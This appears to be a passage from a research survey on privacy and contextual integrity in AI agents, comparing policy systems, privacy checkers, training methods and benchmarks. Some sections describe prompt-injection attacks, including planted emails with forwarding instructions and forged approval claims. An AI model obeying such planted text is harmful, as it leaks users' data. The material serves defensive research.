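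The source of an approval is easy to lose. An agent that notes "the figures are final and legal has signed off" combines a fact with an approval and records the source of neither. As a direction for research, Zhou and Zhang suggest linking each generated claim to its original evidence and to the decisions that its source may influence.

### A policy for each task

Conseca, which Tsai and Bagdasarian (2025), in *Contextual Agent Security*, built at Google, applies a similar separation to the writing of policies. When the user makes a request, a separate language model receives the request, the documentation of the tools and whatever context the developer has marked as trusted. In the prototype this included the date, the list of email addresses and the names of files and folders, but not the contents of emails or files. The model writes a policy that states, for each tool, whether the agent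 may use it, what its inputs must look like and why. The agent then works as usual and can read everything. Before each action, ordinary software checks the call against the policy. A planted email can still mislead the agent, but it can't rewrite the policy. (AirGapAgent, an earlier system, uses a policy for each task to limit which personal data the agent sees.)

One of their example requests is to read unread work emails and answer the urgent ones. The resulting policy allows the agent to send mail only from the user's account, to work addresses, with "urgent" in the subject line, and forbids it to delete anything. The policy sensibly limits the recipients but not the body of the email, so the agent could still send a colleague anything it had read.

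Tsai and Bagdasarian compared Conseca with fixed policies on 20 invented office tasks, using Gemini 1.5 Pro, and averaged the results over five trials:

| Policy | Tasks completed, of 20 | Denied inappropriate actions |
|---|---|---|
| None | 14.0 | No |
| Fixed: everything except deletion | 12.2 | No |
| Fixed: no changes of any kind | 0.0 | Yes |
| Conseca | 12.0 | Yes |

The last column reports a test with one planted email containing an instruction to forward all messages about urgent security vulnerabilities. Without a policy, the agent forwarded them even when the user had only asked it to sort her mail. Conseca blocked the forwarding in every task except one in which the user had asked the agent to perform the tasks in urgent emails. This is encouraging, but a demonstration with one email doesn't measure how secure Conseca is.

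The design has two limits that Tsai and Bagdasarian call fundamental. First, the policy can be no better than the policy model's understanding of the user's preferences, social norms and the task's requirements. Second, the model can't anticipate actions that depend on text it isn't allowed to read. If a user asks the agent to "carry out the tasks requested in my manager's email", she has given that email some authority, but the policy model can't open it to find out which actions to allow.

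Conseca also checks actions one at a time. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that a manipulated agent could reach a harmful result through a series of steps that each look harmless, and that the guarantee assumes a safe policy model. The later system in *Only What You've Signed up For* (2026) depends just as much on the quality of its policy. It also fixes that policy from the user's initial request, so it can't adapt when she legitimately changes her mind halfway through. Google has since added Conseca to its command-line agent as an option that is off by default (*Gemini CLI configuration*).

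### Predicting what the user would permit

A system could also learn the user's preferences from her earlier decisions. In *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, Wu, Yang and colleagues asked 205 people 20 permission questions each, in scenarios from areas such as health, travel and finance. Participants could agree or refuse to share a piece of data, either once or permanently. The predictor first uses collaborative filtering, which suggests answers based on people who made similar choices. A language model then receives the more confident suggestions, along with the user's past choices, demographic details and stated attitudes to privacy, and predicts whether she would allow the request.

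The predictor was right 85.1% of the time, but it granted 15.2% of the requests that users had refused, a high rate for a component meant to protect data. When Wu and colleagues accepted only its most confident predictions, accuracy rose to 94.4%, but these covered 25.9% of requests, and the user had to decide the rest. With no record of the user's past decisions, accuracy was 66.9%. Granting every request would have scored slightly higher, since users had allowed 69% of the requests in the data. A history of one to four queries raised accuracy to 77.7%.

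These figures cover only the "always" and "never" answers. Wu and colleagues left out answers that applied to a single occasion, which made up more than half of the total and were probably the ones in which circumstances mattered most. Accuracy also varied a good deal between people, averaging 69.7% for the least predictable fifth of users and falling to 49% for one person whose choices differed sharply between areas of life. The predictor did particularly badly on payment details, refusing 87.5% of the requests for them that users would have allowed.

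Users' choices may also be the wrong target for prediction. When participants wrongly believed that a tool needed certain data, they shared it about 78% of the time, and a predictor trained on such answers will learn to overshare too. In Zhou and Zhang's terms, a predicted "yes" is evidence about what the user would decide. It becomes permission only if she has authorised the system to act on its predictions, and she can't give that authorisation for a colleague whose medical leave is mentioned in her inbox.

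### When the context is false

Many defences against prompt injection try to keep instructions apart from data. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian think this misses the attacks that will matter most. In their example, an email requests a travel refund and adds that the department head has approved it. The sentence about approval is a claim about the transmission principle, not an instruction, and if it is true, the agent should probably act on it. An attacker can also misstate the sender, argue that the norms favour disclosure, or combine a permitted request with a forbidden one. A defence that stops external text from influencing any action will block legitimate refunds as well as fraudulent ones.

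Two injection detectors did about as well as chance at separating emails that falsely claimed authorisation from nearly identical neutral ones. The detectors were given only the emails, not the user's instruction that made the claims false. A model trained to resist injection sent more unauthorised replies than the model it was based on. In another test, a second model repeatedly revised the deceptive emails, and the share of scenarios in which the agent sent an unauthorised reply rose from under 1% to 96.7%. That test favoured the attacker, who knew the agent's standing instructions and had up to 45 attempts per scenario, while the agent could not check claims and had been told not to ask the user.

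Some failures occurred without an attacker. When a colleague's email combined a permitted internal request with an unauthorised message to an outsider, three models sent the outside message in 6%, 34% and 65% of cases. Telling them that external messages needed approval reduced the rate to zero for two models and 12% for the third.

If an agent sees the same evidence when sending an email is appropriate as when an attacker has faked the context, it must send with the same probability *p* in both situations, however well it reasons. It therefore makes the harmful error of sending in the faked context with probability *p*, and the over-blocking error of refusing in the legitimate one with probability 1 − *p*. Since these probabilities add up to 1, at least one of them is 50% or more.

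The title *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* suggests more than the theorem proves. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian state that the theorem does not show that such a pair of situations exists in every deployment, and that verification can remove the ambiguity. For example, if the agent can look up the refund in the approvals system, the two situations no longer look the same. They expect unverifiable claims to become more common as agents gain autonomy, which is plausible but still a forecast.

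A security engineer could fairly reply that an agent doesn't need to recognise a lie that it can't act on. Silverlock's reconciliation agent has no general tool for sending messages, so a forged approval can't make it email the ledger to a stranger. There is good evidence that such limits work. *NOMOS* (2026) turns written policies into checks on tool calls and tests them on AgentDojo, a standard set of injection attacks. With one of the two models tested, attacks on an unprotected agent succeeded in 46.5% of banking cases and 70.5% of cases in Slack, a workplace chat program. With the checks in place, no attack that the benchmark counts led to a malicious action in either set, and the highest rate in any of the four sets was 1.4%.

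The attacks succeeded for different reasons. Both models created a calendar event that an attacker had planted, because the software check was weaker than the written rule it was meant to enforce. The benchmark's count also omits nine cases in which one model carried out deletions ordered by an attacker, and some planted payments that went to payees already known to the system. One case did depend on context. The agent emailed the user's passport and card numbers to an address she had named in her request. The recipient was authorised and the written policy did not forbid the message, so preventing it would have required judging whether that recipient should have those numbers.

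## Using a language model to judge whether sharing is appropriate

The agent broke no written rule when it emailed its user's passport and card numbers to the address she had named. Nobody can write a rule for every combination of recipient and information, so several research groups have let a language model judge each disclosure as it arises. Models usually answer well when asked directly whether a disclosure is acceptable, but nobody asks an agent this while it is drafting an email. The main methods differ in how they put the question to the model and in what they do with the answer.

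### How PrivacyLens tests an agent

Researchers have tested most of these methods on *PrivacyLens* (Shao, Li and colleagues, 2024), a benchmark built from 493 information flows that break a privacy norm. In one, John's agent emails John's manager that John is talking to other companies about a new job. The flows come from crowdsourcing, US privacy regulations and research on vulnerable groups, and at least two of three annotators had to consider each one privacy-sensitive. GPT-4 expanded each flow into a short story and then into a record of an agent's work, which includes simulated calendar entries and emails but stops before the final step. The model under test writes that step, such as the email to the manager, and a second model checks whether a reader could infer any of the sensitive items from it. The leakage rate is the share of cases in which a reader could infer at least one.

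The benchmark also includes direct questions about whether the same flows are acceptable. In *Privacy in Action*, Wang, Yu and colleagues (2025) repeated both tests with a prompt that told the model to be discreet. The model classified the information as sensitive 98.0% of the time but leaked it in 33.1% of cases. When it leaked information, its written reasoning rarely mentioned privacy and dealt only with finishing the task.

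Shao and colleagues designed PrivacyLens around worst cases, with vague instructions and sensitive data close at hand, so a leakage rate of 33% doesn't mean that a third of ordinary emails leak. Every case also contains something to withhold, so the right answer to every direct question is "no". The 98.0% score on those questions may therefore partly reflect a tendency to answer "no". Over-blocking shows up only in a separate helpfulness score, which another model assigns on a scale from 0 to 3.

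### A supervisor for each field of a form

Forms are easier to start with than emails because each field names the information requested. Ghalebikesabi, Bagdasaryan and colleagues, in *Operationalizing Contextual Integrity in Privacy-Conscious Assistants* (2024; journal version, *Privacy Awareness for Information-Sharing Assistants*, 2025), built assistants that fill in web forms from a profile with 51 kinds of personal information. In the simplest design, one model fills in the form and leaves blank any field it considers inappropriate to fill. In the others, a "supervisor" model first decides whether each field should be filled, and a separate "filler" never receives the fields the supervisor rejects.

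The most elaborate supervisor first writes an "information flow card" that lists the five parameters of the flow, along with the wider context, the relationship between the parties and the purpose. The supervisor then chooses whether to fill the field, leave it blank or ask the user.

To score these decisions, eight people judged which kinds of information were necessary for 14 kinds of form, such as a bank account application or a clothes shop's newsletter sign-up. Information counted as necessary for a form only if none of them disagreed, but where a law settled the matter, it overrode their answers. About a quarter of the combinations of form and information remained unclear, and the correct decision for those was to ask the user.

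With Google's Gemini Ultra, the single model filled 21% of the fields it should have left blank and correctly filled 79% of those it should have filled. The supervisor with flow cards reduced the first figure to 1% and raised the second to 86%. Gemma 2 27B, a smaller open model, filled every field it should have left blank when it worked alone. The supervisor stopped this leakage but reduced the share of necessary fields filled correctly from 90% to 66%. The wording of the supervisor's prompt also affected both rates. With Gemini Pro, a supervisor that explained its decisions without a flow card leaked nothing but filled only 56% of the necessary fields, while one with a card leaked 4% and filled 72%.

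These tests were simpler than real use. Each field needed only one entry from the profile, the assistants handled fields one at a time, and no third party tried to deceive them. An email has no fields, so a model must work out what information the message would share, and with whom, before it can judge whether sharing it is appropriate.

### PrivacyChecker: listing and judging the flows

Wang and colleagues' PrivacyChecker adds instructions for judging information flows to the agent's prompt. The model lists each information flow in the user's request, the tool results and the earlier conversation, along with the flow's five parameters. It then marks each flow as appropriate or not with a "yes" or "no" and a brief reason. An operator can add guidelines, such as a rule never to share phone numbers. The model then writes its message, omitting or generalising anything marked "no". Microsoft's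 blog post *Reducing Privacy leaks in AI*, which covers this method and a training method, gives the example of an agent that may share a résumé but not a Social Security number when replying to an email.

On PrivacyLens, PrivacyChecker reduced GPT-4o's leakage rate from 33.06% to 8.32%, while its helpfulness score fell from 2.69 to 2.45. DeepSeek-R1's leakage rate fell by a similar amount, from 36.08% to 7.30%, but Qwen3-8B, a much smaller model, still leaked in 24.20% of cases with PrivacyChecker when its reasoning mode was off. Wang and colleagues also ran the form-filling supervisor on the benchmark. With GPT-4o, it leaked more often than PrivacyChecker (14.4% of cases) but was slightly more helpful (2.52).

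Part of the benefit comes from writing the judgements down. When the model made them silently, leakage rose from 8.32% to 11.36% for GPT-4o and from 15.91% to 30.63% for Qwen3-14B. Giving the model the correct flow from the dataset instead of its own list roughly halved GPT-4o's leakage, to 4.26%. Wang and colleagues conclude that better extraction would help. But the flows in the dataset are the inappropriate ones, so supplying one may also have shown the model which flow was the problem.

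In 18 of the 36 leaks that remained with DeepSeek-R1, the model had listed the sensitive flow but judged it acceptable. In three it had missed the flow, and four involved errors by the model that scored the results. In the other 11, DeepSeek-R1 had correctly decided to withhold the information but then disclosed it anyway. These 11 leaks show a weakness of having one model judge the information and write the message in the same pass. The form-filling assistant avoids this weakness because the filler never receives a field that the supervisor has rejected.

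### Three places to install the check

Wang and colleagues also rebuilt 150 of the PrivacyLens cases as PrivacyLens-Live, in which agents use working Gmail and Notion accounts through the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting models to tools. OpenAI's o3, with only the instruction to be discreet, leaked in 17.4% of the static cases and 26.3% of the live ones. Live searches often failed or returned clutter. In one case, the user wanted to share a public presentation, but the agent retrieved and used a confidential strategic plan.

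They tried PrivacyChecker in three places:

- **In the agent's standing instructions.** The check applies to everything the agent does, but it may miss details when the context is long.
- **In the description of one tool**, such as the one that sends email. Each tool can have its own rules, but developers can't easily reuse them for other tools.
- **As a separate tool.** The agent submits its draft and the record of its work, and needs approval before it sends the message. This leaves a log that auditors can read but takes more maintenance.

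All three reduced live leakage to between 5.3% and 8.7%. The separate tool had the lowest rate when one agent worked alone (5.3%) and the highest when the sender and the recipient each had an agent (8.7%). These rates correspond to 8 and 13 leaks in 150 cases, so they are a poor basis for choosing. A better reason to prefer the separate tool is that it produces an explicit decision, which ordinary software could use to block any unapproved message. A check inside the agent's instructions works only if the agent follows them.

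PrivacyChecker did less well on 36 new cases that added a third tool, such as a calendar or Slack. It reduced o3's leakage only from 22.6% to 16.4% in the static version and from 28.6% to 16.7% in the live version. Wang and colleagues found that the model often missed flows or described them ambiguously. The extra tool may not fully explain the weaker results, because the new cases also differ in content and each one accounts for almost three percentage points. Still, most office agents have more than three tools, and a check that depends on a complete list of flows is likely to get harder with more sources.

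### Training a model to make the judgement

Lan, Inan and colleagues (2025), in *Contextual Integrity in LLMs via Reasoning and Reinforcement Learning*, also began with a prompt. Before writing its answer, the model is instructed to describe the task and its context, then decide whether sharing each personal detail is necessary, helpful, optional or inappropriate. The prompt made models more cautious in general. With Gemini 2.5 Flash, for example, leakage on PrivacyLens fell from 29.0% to 19.7%, but helpfulness also fell, from 2.75 to 2.31.

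They then used reinforcement learning to teach models to withhold less of the information a task needs. The model writes several answers to the same request, a program scores them, and training makes the higher-scoring answers more likely. The thesis *Reinforcement Learning for Scalable and Trustworthy Intelligent Systems* describes the data and the scoring in full. They used GPT-4 to generate about 700 examples and trained on 590 of them. Each example combined a setting such as email, a domain such as healthcare, and one of three transmission principles: confidentiality, proportionality or consent. GPT-4 listed the information the task required and the information the principle restricted, then wrote a realistic request that mixed the two without labels.

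The program scores an answer by searching it for keywords from the two lists:

```
R = (required keywords present / all required keywords)
    − (restricted keywords present / all restricted keywords)

R = −1 if the answer does not follow the prescribed format
```

For example, booking an event might require a name, a date and the number of guests, while the user's finances and medical history are restricted, with one keyword for each item. A message with only the three required items scores 1. Adding the medical history lowers the score to 0.5, while leaving out the number of guests lowers it to about 0.67. A message that discloses everything scores 0, as does one that discloses nothing. The model therefore can't earn a good score by withholding everything, and developers can change the weights if they consider a leak worse than an omission.

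Microsoft's post gives the results on PrivacyLens for four open models:

| Model | Leakage: original / prompt / training | Helpfulness: original / prompt / training |
|---|---|---|
| Mistral-7B | 47.9% / 28.8% / 31.1% | 1.78 / 1.17 / 1.84 |
| Qwen2.5-7B | 50.3% / 44.8% / 33.7% | 1.99 / 2.13 / 2.08 |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 18.2% / 21.3% / 18.5% | 1.05 / 1.29 / 1.18 |
| Qwen2.5-14B | 52.9% / 42.8% / 33.9% | 2.37 / 2.27 / 2.30 |

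Microsoft presents training as a way to recover the helpfulness that models lose when given the prompt. Mistral's results fit this description well. The two Qwen models had lost little or no helpfulness, and training mainly reduced their leakage further. Training did not reduce Llama's overall leakage, which was already low. But Llama's helpfulness score of 1.05 before training means that it often failed at the task, so its low leakage is not evidence that it chose well what to share. Among its helpful answers, leakage fell from 38.9% to 29.4%.

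Keyword scoring takes little compute and is easy to inspect, but it misses paraphrases. If the restricted keyword is "divorce", an email saying that a colleague's marriage has ended incurs no penalty. Tamber, Puri and colleagues (2026), in *PrivacyAlign*, criticise keyword-based rewards for this reason and base theirs on human judgements. They had 599 people compare pairs of drafts, mark what each draft leaked or wrongly omitted, and explain their choices. During training, a judge model reads the annotators' comments on a request before it compares new answers to the same request. This brings the reward closer to what people object to, although the annotators disagreed about leaks in roughly a fifth of comparisons.

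### Dividing the work among several models

A single model that must find the sensitive information, judge it and write the message may do one of these jobs badly. In *1-2-3 Check*, Li, Sun and colleagues (2026) divide the jobs among three models. An extractor lists the events in a text, a checker classifies each as private or public, and an executor writes the message. They tested this mainly on a meeting-summary task from ConfAIde, an earlier privacy benchmark. In this task, three people discuss a secret about a colleague, who joins the meeting later. The summary must leave out the secret but include the public information that the colleague missed.

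The results for GPT-4o show how easily a method can exchange one error for the other:

| Arrangement | Leaked the secret | Omitted public information | Made either error |
|---|---|---|---|
| One model | 23.0% | 12.0% | 26.3% |
| One model, told to follow the same steps | 2.0% | 32.5% | 34.0% |
| Three models, executor sees labels and transcript | 5.0% | 20.0% | 24.5% |
| Three models, executor sees labels only | 8.5% | 10.0% | 17.5% |

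The single model with step-by-step instructions leaked by far the least, but it left out public information in almost a third of summaries and so made more errors overall than the model without those instructions. Hiding the transcript from the executor gave the best overall result for GPT-4o. For Llama-3.1-70B, the best result came when the checker forwarded only the public items and the executor kept the transcript, which reduced the combined error rate from 48.5% to 20.5%. Li, Sun and colleagues tried eight multi-model arrangements for each model on the same task, and most of the combined rates have standard errors of five to eight percentage points. The evidence that these arrangements can outperform a single unaided model is therefore stronger than the evidence for how they rank against each other.

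The pipeline also raised the share of PrivacyLens cases without a leak by 15 to 19 percentage points for GPT-4o and GPT-4.1, with almost no loss of helpfulness. With o3 that share exceeded 92%, but helpfulness was below 1.6, so it probably avoided many of the leaks by not doing the task properly. Running three models in sequence is slower and more expensive than running one, and developers must write the extractor's categories and the checker's privacy rules separately for each field, such as medicine or finance.

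### The same methods on newer models

Better models still need these checks. *PiSAs* (Gupta, Mohammadi Sepahvand and colleagues, 2026) tested eight recent models on 265 invented workplace tasks. In each task, a written policy determines which facts should affect a decision, such as whether a hospital should discharge a patient. The agent has to gather the relevant facts and then decide. It never needs the inappropriate facts to solve the task, and the violation rate is the share of them that it gathers in at least one of three runs. When a single agent had access to all the data and a strong instruction to protect privacy, violation rates ranged from 19.3% for GPT-6 Astra to 49.5% for Kimi-K2.5. Claude Fable 5.1 gathered the largest share of the facts the tasks needed, 98.7%, but also 40.3% of the inappropriate ones.

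They then added PrivacyChecker to GPT-5.6 Sol, which cut violations from 24.8% to about 6%, a reduction similar to the one on GPT-4o in 2025. But the agent also gathered only 77.9% of the facts it needed, down from 97.0%. Similar omissions may have been missed on PrivacyLens, where helpfulness fell only slightly, since a judge can rate an email as good without noticing that a useful detail is missing.

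Outside researchers can't retrain the leading closed models, so the newer tests of reinforcement learning use small open ones. *It Takes Two* (2026), from the Korean university KAIST and the company DeepAuto.ai, repeated Lan and colleagues' training on several of them. On PrivacyLens, leakage fell only from 56.6% to 53.8% for Qwen3-4B-Instruct and rose from 25.8% to 28.2% for Olmo-3-7B-Instruct. The study attributes such weak results to giving each answer a single score, which combines two different demands and gives the model little information about which detail was wrong.

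Its alternative, SELFCI, has the model explain why each required item belongs in the answer and why each restricted item does not. Two copies of the model then act as teachers. One is given the reasons for sharing and the other the reasons for withholding, and the model is trained towards answers that both teachers assign high probability to. This reduced Qwen3-4B-Instruct's leakage to 47.1% without making it less helpful. Training towards only one teacher made the model again withhold too much or disclose too much, depending on the teacher.

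Training on human judgements has not yet produced a model that is competitive with the leading ones. Gupta and colleagues tested a four-billion-parameter model that Tamber and colleagues had trained. It included 76.2% of the inappropriate facts and only 75.1% of the necessary ones. Its small size probably explains much of this poor performance, so the result is stronger evidence about using such a model on its own than about the training method.

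Without PrivacyChecker, GPT-5.6 Sol's remaining leaks were concentrated in facts that looked relevant. The model included only 0.2% of the personal facts that had nothing to do with the task, but 42.9% of those that seemed relevant to the decision but weren't. It also passed on 35.7% of the private details attached to something the task needed, such as the medical appointment that makes an employee unavailable from 10 to 11. Deciding whether to share or withhold the whole sentence doesn't work here, because sharing it discloses the appointment and withholding it leaves out the unavailability. On one set of tasks, Gupta and colleagues supplied a version of each such fact without the private detail, along with a note on its sensitivity, and violations fell substantially. But they point out that whoever prepares those versions has already made the judgement the model was supposed to make.

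## How reliable these judgements are

How far an operator can rely on a model's judgement depends on why the model gets cases wrong. The context may lack a deciding fact. It may contain all the facts but leave out a decision made elsewhere that the norm depends on. The model may answer differently when someone repeats or rewords the question. People may also disagree about a case, so no answer would satisfy everyone. These four problems need different remedies, but a single error rate combines them.

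### From invented secrets to office work

*Can LLMs Keep a Secret?* (2023) introduced ConfAIde, the first benchmark to test whether language models respect contextual integrity. In one test, the model writes what a person who knows someone's secret says to a third person, who doesn't know it but could benefit from hearing it. Niloofar Mireshghallah, the benchmark's lead author, reports in *From Black and White to Gray* that GPT-4 revealed private information 39% of the time, and ChatGPT 57%, in situations where people would have kept it to themselves. In 51% of the errors, the model had acknowledged that something was private.

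Agents can recognise a risk and still disclose the information. *Trilemma* (2026) examined the reasoning of 38 agents that had each disclosed something confidential about the employee they represented. They usually identified the risk correctly in general terms but did not check the sentence they sent against it. Some found reasons to dismiss the risk, including one that reasoned that revealing its employee's lack of preparation would protect her if the task went badly. Leakage rates for agents therefore include failures to act on a correct judgement as well as wrong judgements.

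*CI-Work* (Fu, Qin and colleagues, 2026) tested nine models on 125 invented workplace tasks. In one, a manager asks an agent to send an employee a summary of the problems in his recent code. The agent's searches return four items that the message needs and four related ones that the recipient shouldn't see. Disclosing any of the second four counts as a violation. Violation rates ranged from 15.8% for DeepSeek-R1 to 50.9% for Grok-3. But DeepSeek-R1 also conveyed only 53.1% of the necessary items, so its low violation rate partly reflects how much its messages left out. GPT-5 conveyed 93.0% of the necessary items and had a violation rate of 27.8%.

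The models took rough account of rank and company boundaries, leaking less when managers wrote to staff than when staff reported to their superiors, and generally less to outsiders than to colleagues. They were worse at matching a particular item to a particular recipient. For example, they might reveal a walk-away price during a negotiation. Larger versions of GPT-4.1 conveyed more of the information the task needed but also leaked more, and raising GPT-5's reasoning effort reduced violations only slightly. Instructing GPT-5 to consider the roles of sender and recipient reduced its violation rate to 22.1%, but the share of necessary items it conveyed also fell, to 84.9%.

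Fu and colleagues also found that pressure from the user nearly doubled GPT-5's violation rate. This result is harder to interpret than the others because, in their example of strong pressure, the user is a manager who tells the agent to mention that she may delay the employee's promotion. An agent that includes this has obeyed its user, and whether it should have refused depends as much on her authority as on privacy. Apart from this problem, the violation rates are probably slightly too low. In 38 of the 43 cases where the model that scored the messages disagreed with the majority of three human checkers, the people had found a disclosure and the model had not.

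Newer agents have the same problem. *AgentCIScope* (Guo, Chen and colleagues, 2026) tested 12 agents on 936 tasks in working copies of applications such as email, calendars and chat. The share of tasks with a leak ranged from 32.5% for Claude Opus 5 running in Claude Code to 94.4% for Gemini 3.8 Flash. These are stress-test rates, because the instructions imitate requests that tend to cause leaks, such as asking for a self-contained briefing. On average, agents leaked credit card details, which are recognisable in any context, in 17.1% of cases. They leaked personal preferences, which are sensitive only in some contexts, in 84.7%.

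Agents that are good at their tasks can still leak information. *Capable but Careless* (2026) tested agents that operate a computer's ordinary applications. Among those that completed more than 75% of their tasks, leakage (not counting refusals) ranged from 14.0% for Claude Opus 4.7 to 98.3% for Gemini 3.1 Pro.

### Missing and misread facts

Some test cases describe a situation too briefly for anyone to judge it. *Privacy Reasoning in Ambiguous Contexts* (Yi, Suciu and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of an insurance agent who sends a coworker clients' insurance information in a Slack message. The benchmark labels this inappropriate, but Gemini 2.5 Pro called it appropriate, assuming the company had its usual security measures in place. The right answer depends on what the information includes, whether the coworker needs it and whether the company allows it on Slack, none of which the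 description states.

PrivacyLens and ConfAIde contain only inappropriate flows, so Yi and colleagues added an appropriate counterpart for each flow. They asked three models whether each flow was acceptable. On the PrivacyLens set, 86% to 92% of the models' "yes" answers were correct, but the models rejected 24% to 37% of the appropriate flows. Models that leak information when they write an email can therefore be too strict when asked directly whether a flow is acceptable.

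Filling in the missing details raised the share of "yes" answers that were correct by up to 13.3% and the share of appropriate flows that the models allowed by up to 22.3%. Some of the added details nearly gave away the answer, such as a note that an alumnus's record was marked "do not disclose", so these gains are probably close to the best that clarification could achieve. A working agent would have to get the missing fact from its user or a database, and either could be wrong.

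Models can also misread facts that they have. Ebead, Formanek and Leibo (2026), in *A Generative Model of Contextual Integrity*, simulated conversations in which one model played a person with private information, such as a bank account number or home address, and another tried to obtain it. In one scenario, a billing office needs a student's bank details to pay a refund, but the person asking for them is a fellow student. Some of the holders also had memories that made them trusting or sceptical. The table gives the number of conversations, out of 27 of each kind, in which the holder shared the information:

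| Situation | No added disposition | Trusting | Sceptical |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nobody needs the information, and the asker has no relevant role | 0 | 14 | 0 |
| Nobody needs it here, but the asker handles such information elsewhere | 2 | 24 | 3 |
| Someone needs it, but not the asker | 16 | 17 | 12 |
| The asker needs it and is entitled to it | 27 | 27 | 22 |

With no added disposition, the holder almost always refused when nobody needed the information. But when someone else needed it, the holder gave it to the wrong person in 16 of 27 conversations, and three other models did so in 12 to 18. The real need apparently made the request look legitimate, whoever made it. A sceptical holder made this mistake somewhat less often, but it also refused 5 of 27 legitimate requests. Software could have decided the refund case by checking whether the asker worked in the billing office.

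These models played private individuals guarding their own data, rather than agents working for a user. Each group of 27 conversations comes from only nine scenarios, each run three times, and the activities differ between the four situations. Claude Haiku 4.5 refused to take part at all, even in a scenario where a university needed a student's bank details to pay a stipend.

When data concerns several people, a model must also work out who they are, because it can't consider whether someone has agreed to the disclosure if it overlooks them. *IDP-Bench* (Hussain, Vincent and colleagues, 2026) gave eight open models 97 short scenarios about material such as group photos, contact lists and meeting notes. More than 90% of the time, six of the models recognised that the data belonged to several people. But seven of the eight correctly identified the other people affected no more than about 74%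 of the time.

The two largest Qwen models rated the sharing inappropriate in at least 91% of their answers, even though they often failed to identify whom it would affect. The expected answer was "no" in every scenario, so a model could get a perfect score by always answering "no". All eight models date from 2024, and one of them also generated the scenarios and was one of the two judges.

### Norms that a document does not contain

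A model may have every relevant fact and still lack information about what an organisation has decided. Thornton and colleagues tested this with the invented clinic whose documents their software releases only to permitted requesters. From each document's label, the software uses a sensitivity tier, such as "financial", and a list of the roles that may receive the document. A person had written the labels for all 105 documents. Thornton and colleagues had a language model write them instead and kept everything else fixed, including the records of which staff were assigned to which patients. The software then decided the same 2,520 flows (24 requesters times 105 documents). Under the original labels, it permits 259 and refuses 2,261.

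Each model received a document's title, type, subject and full text, along with definitions of the tiers and roles. The instructions told it to grant as few roles as necessary, and even specified that only doctors may receive mental-health records. The last column of the table compares five identical labelling runs, while the other columns describe the first run:

| Model | Tier matched | Role list matched | Wrongful releases (of 2,261) | Over-blocks (of 259) | Decisions that changed between runs |
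|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 78% | 55% | 40 (1.8%) | 31 (12%) | 115 |
| Claude Opus 4.8, extended thinking off | 83% | 57% | 44 (1.9%) | 27 (10%) | 108 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 82% | 52% | 64 (2.8%) | 34 (13%) | 96 |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 84% | 30% | 39 (1.7%) | 28 (11%) | 124 |
| GPT-5.4 | 86% | 23% | 9 (0.4%) | 100 (39%) | 40 |
| GPT-5.4-mini | 83% | 80% | 11 (0.5%) | 26 (10%) | 28 |
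| GPT-5.4-nano | 82% | 69% | 16 (0.7%) | 36 (14%) | 13 |

The models matched the tier on 78% to 86% of documents but the exact list of roles on only 23% to 80%. A document's type nearly determines its tier, since for 19 of the clinic's 21 document types, every document of that type has the same tier. But a model can't tell from a document's text who the clinic has decided may read it. For example, a request for an insurer to approve a treatment may contain both a diagnosis and billing codes, but not whether the billing staff may see the diagnosis. Thornton and colleagues traced every wrongful release to an error in the list of roles.

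GPT-5.4 wrongly released only 9 of the 2,261 forbidden flows (0.4%), but it wrongly blocked 100 of the 259 permitted flows (39%), so people at this clinic would lose more than a third of the access they are entitled to. Its labels led to the right decision for 95.7% of all 2,520 flows, only six percentage points more than the 89.7% that software would achieve by refusing every request.

The release rates are also low because the software still checks the human-written assignments, and this check catches many labelling errors. An organisation that relied on roles alone would probably make more wrongful releases with the same labels.

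In a second experiment, the norms came from a published law, HIPAA. Thornton and colleagues took 214 flows from US court cases about HIPAA in PrivaCI-Bench, a benchmark based on regulations and court decisions. Each model judged whether HIPAA permitted the flow, prohibited it or did not apply. GPT-5.4-mini did best, agreeing with the label derived from the court's decision in 87.8% of cases. But the law prohibited only 20 of the 214 flows, and GPT-5.4-mini called 11 of those permitted. A model that never recognised a violation but got the other 194 flows right would score higher, at 90.7%. For anyone who wants to prevent improper disclosures, the share of prohibited flows called permitted matters more than overall accuracy, although with only 20 cases the true share could plausibly be anywhere from about a third to three quarters.

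The clinic experiment used synthetic documents from a single field and assumed that everyone acts in good faith. Its most serious limit is that one annotator wrote all the labels. A second person following the same instructions might have written different lists, so a mismatch between a model's answer and the labels could be a mistake by the model or a reasonable difference of opinion. The models also had only general guidance about who should see what, so the experiment doesn't show how well they would apply a detailed written policy.

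### The same question, a different answer

Relying on one annotator doesn't affect comparisons of a model with itself. When Thornton and colleagues had each model label the documents five times with identical inputs, the models gave between 87% and 99% of the documents the same tier every time. The least consistent model gave only 26% of them the same list of roles every time. Between 13 and 124 of the 2,520 access decisions changed from run to run. Labels from Claude Opus 4.8 caused 34 wrongful releases in one run and 57 in another. A clinic that labels its documents once will get one of these outcomes by chance. If it has a model judge every request instead, someone the model refuses may succeed by asking again.

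A consistent model isn't necessarily safe. GPT-5.4-nano had the fewest unstable decisions, but 9 of its 13 concerned flows that the clinic forbids. GPT-5.4 had 40, none of which concerned forbidden flows. Comparing the two companies' models is unfair because the Claude models ran at default settings, which allow random variation, while the OpenAI models mostly ran at a setting that reduces it. A majority vote over the five runs still produced 33 wrongful releases for Claude Opus 4.8 and 66 for Claude Sonnet 5, and Sonnet's 66 was more than in any of its single runs. Voting can correct occasional errors, but it preserves any error that a model makes in most runs.

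Agents' actions vary too. When Guo and colleagues repeated each task five times, leakage rates rose by 4 to 19 percentage points. The same model's rate could also differ by more than ten points depending on the software framework that ran it.

The wording of the question also affects the model's judgements. When Yi and colleagues added a sentence asking Gemini 2.5 Pro to consider privacy norms, the share of appropriate flows it allowed fell from 69.0% to 40.6%, while the share of its "yes" answers that were correct rose only from 86.5% to 91.3%. Asking it instead to share as much as possible while respecting privacy also lowered the share of appropriate flows it allowed, to 63.5%. An operator therefore can't predict an instruction's effect from its wording, and has to test it on both appropriate and inappropriate flows.

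### When people disagree

Human checkers often disagree about what an agent may share. Fu and colleagues had three office workers judge 200 items from 25 of their tasks, and each pair agreed on 81% to 88.5% of them. These items were relatively clear, because the researchers had used a model to find and rewrite ambiguous ones. Tamber and colleagues used cases on which agents actually leak, and found 78.4% agreement about leaks and 75.8% about omissions.

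Such percentages overstate consensus when one answer is much more common than the other. Researchers therefore also report Cohen's kappa, which is 0 for agreement at the level of chance and 1 for perfect agreement:

```
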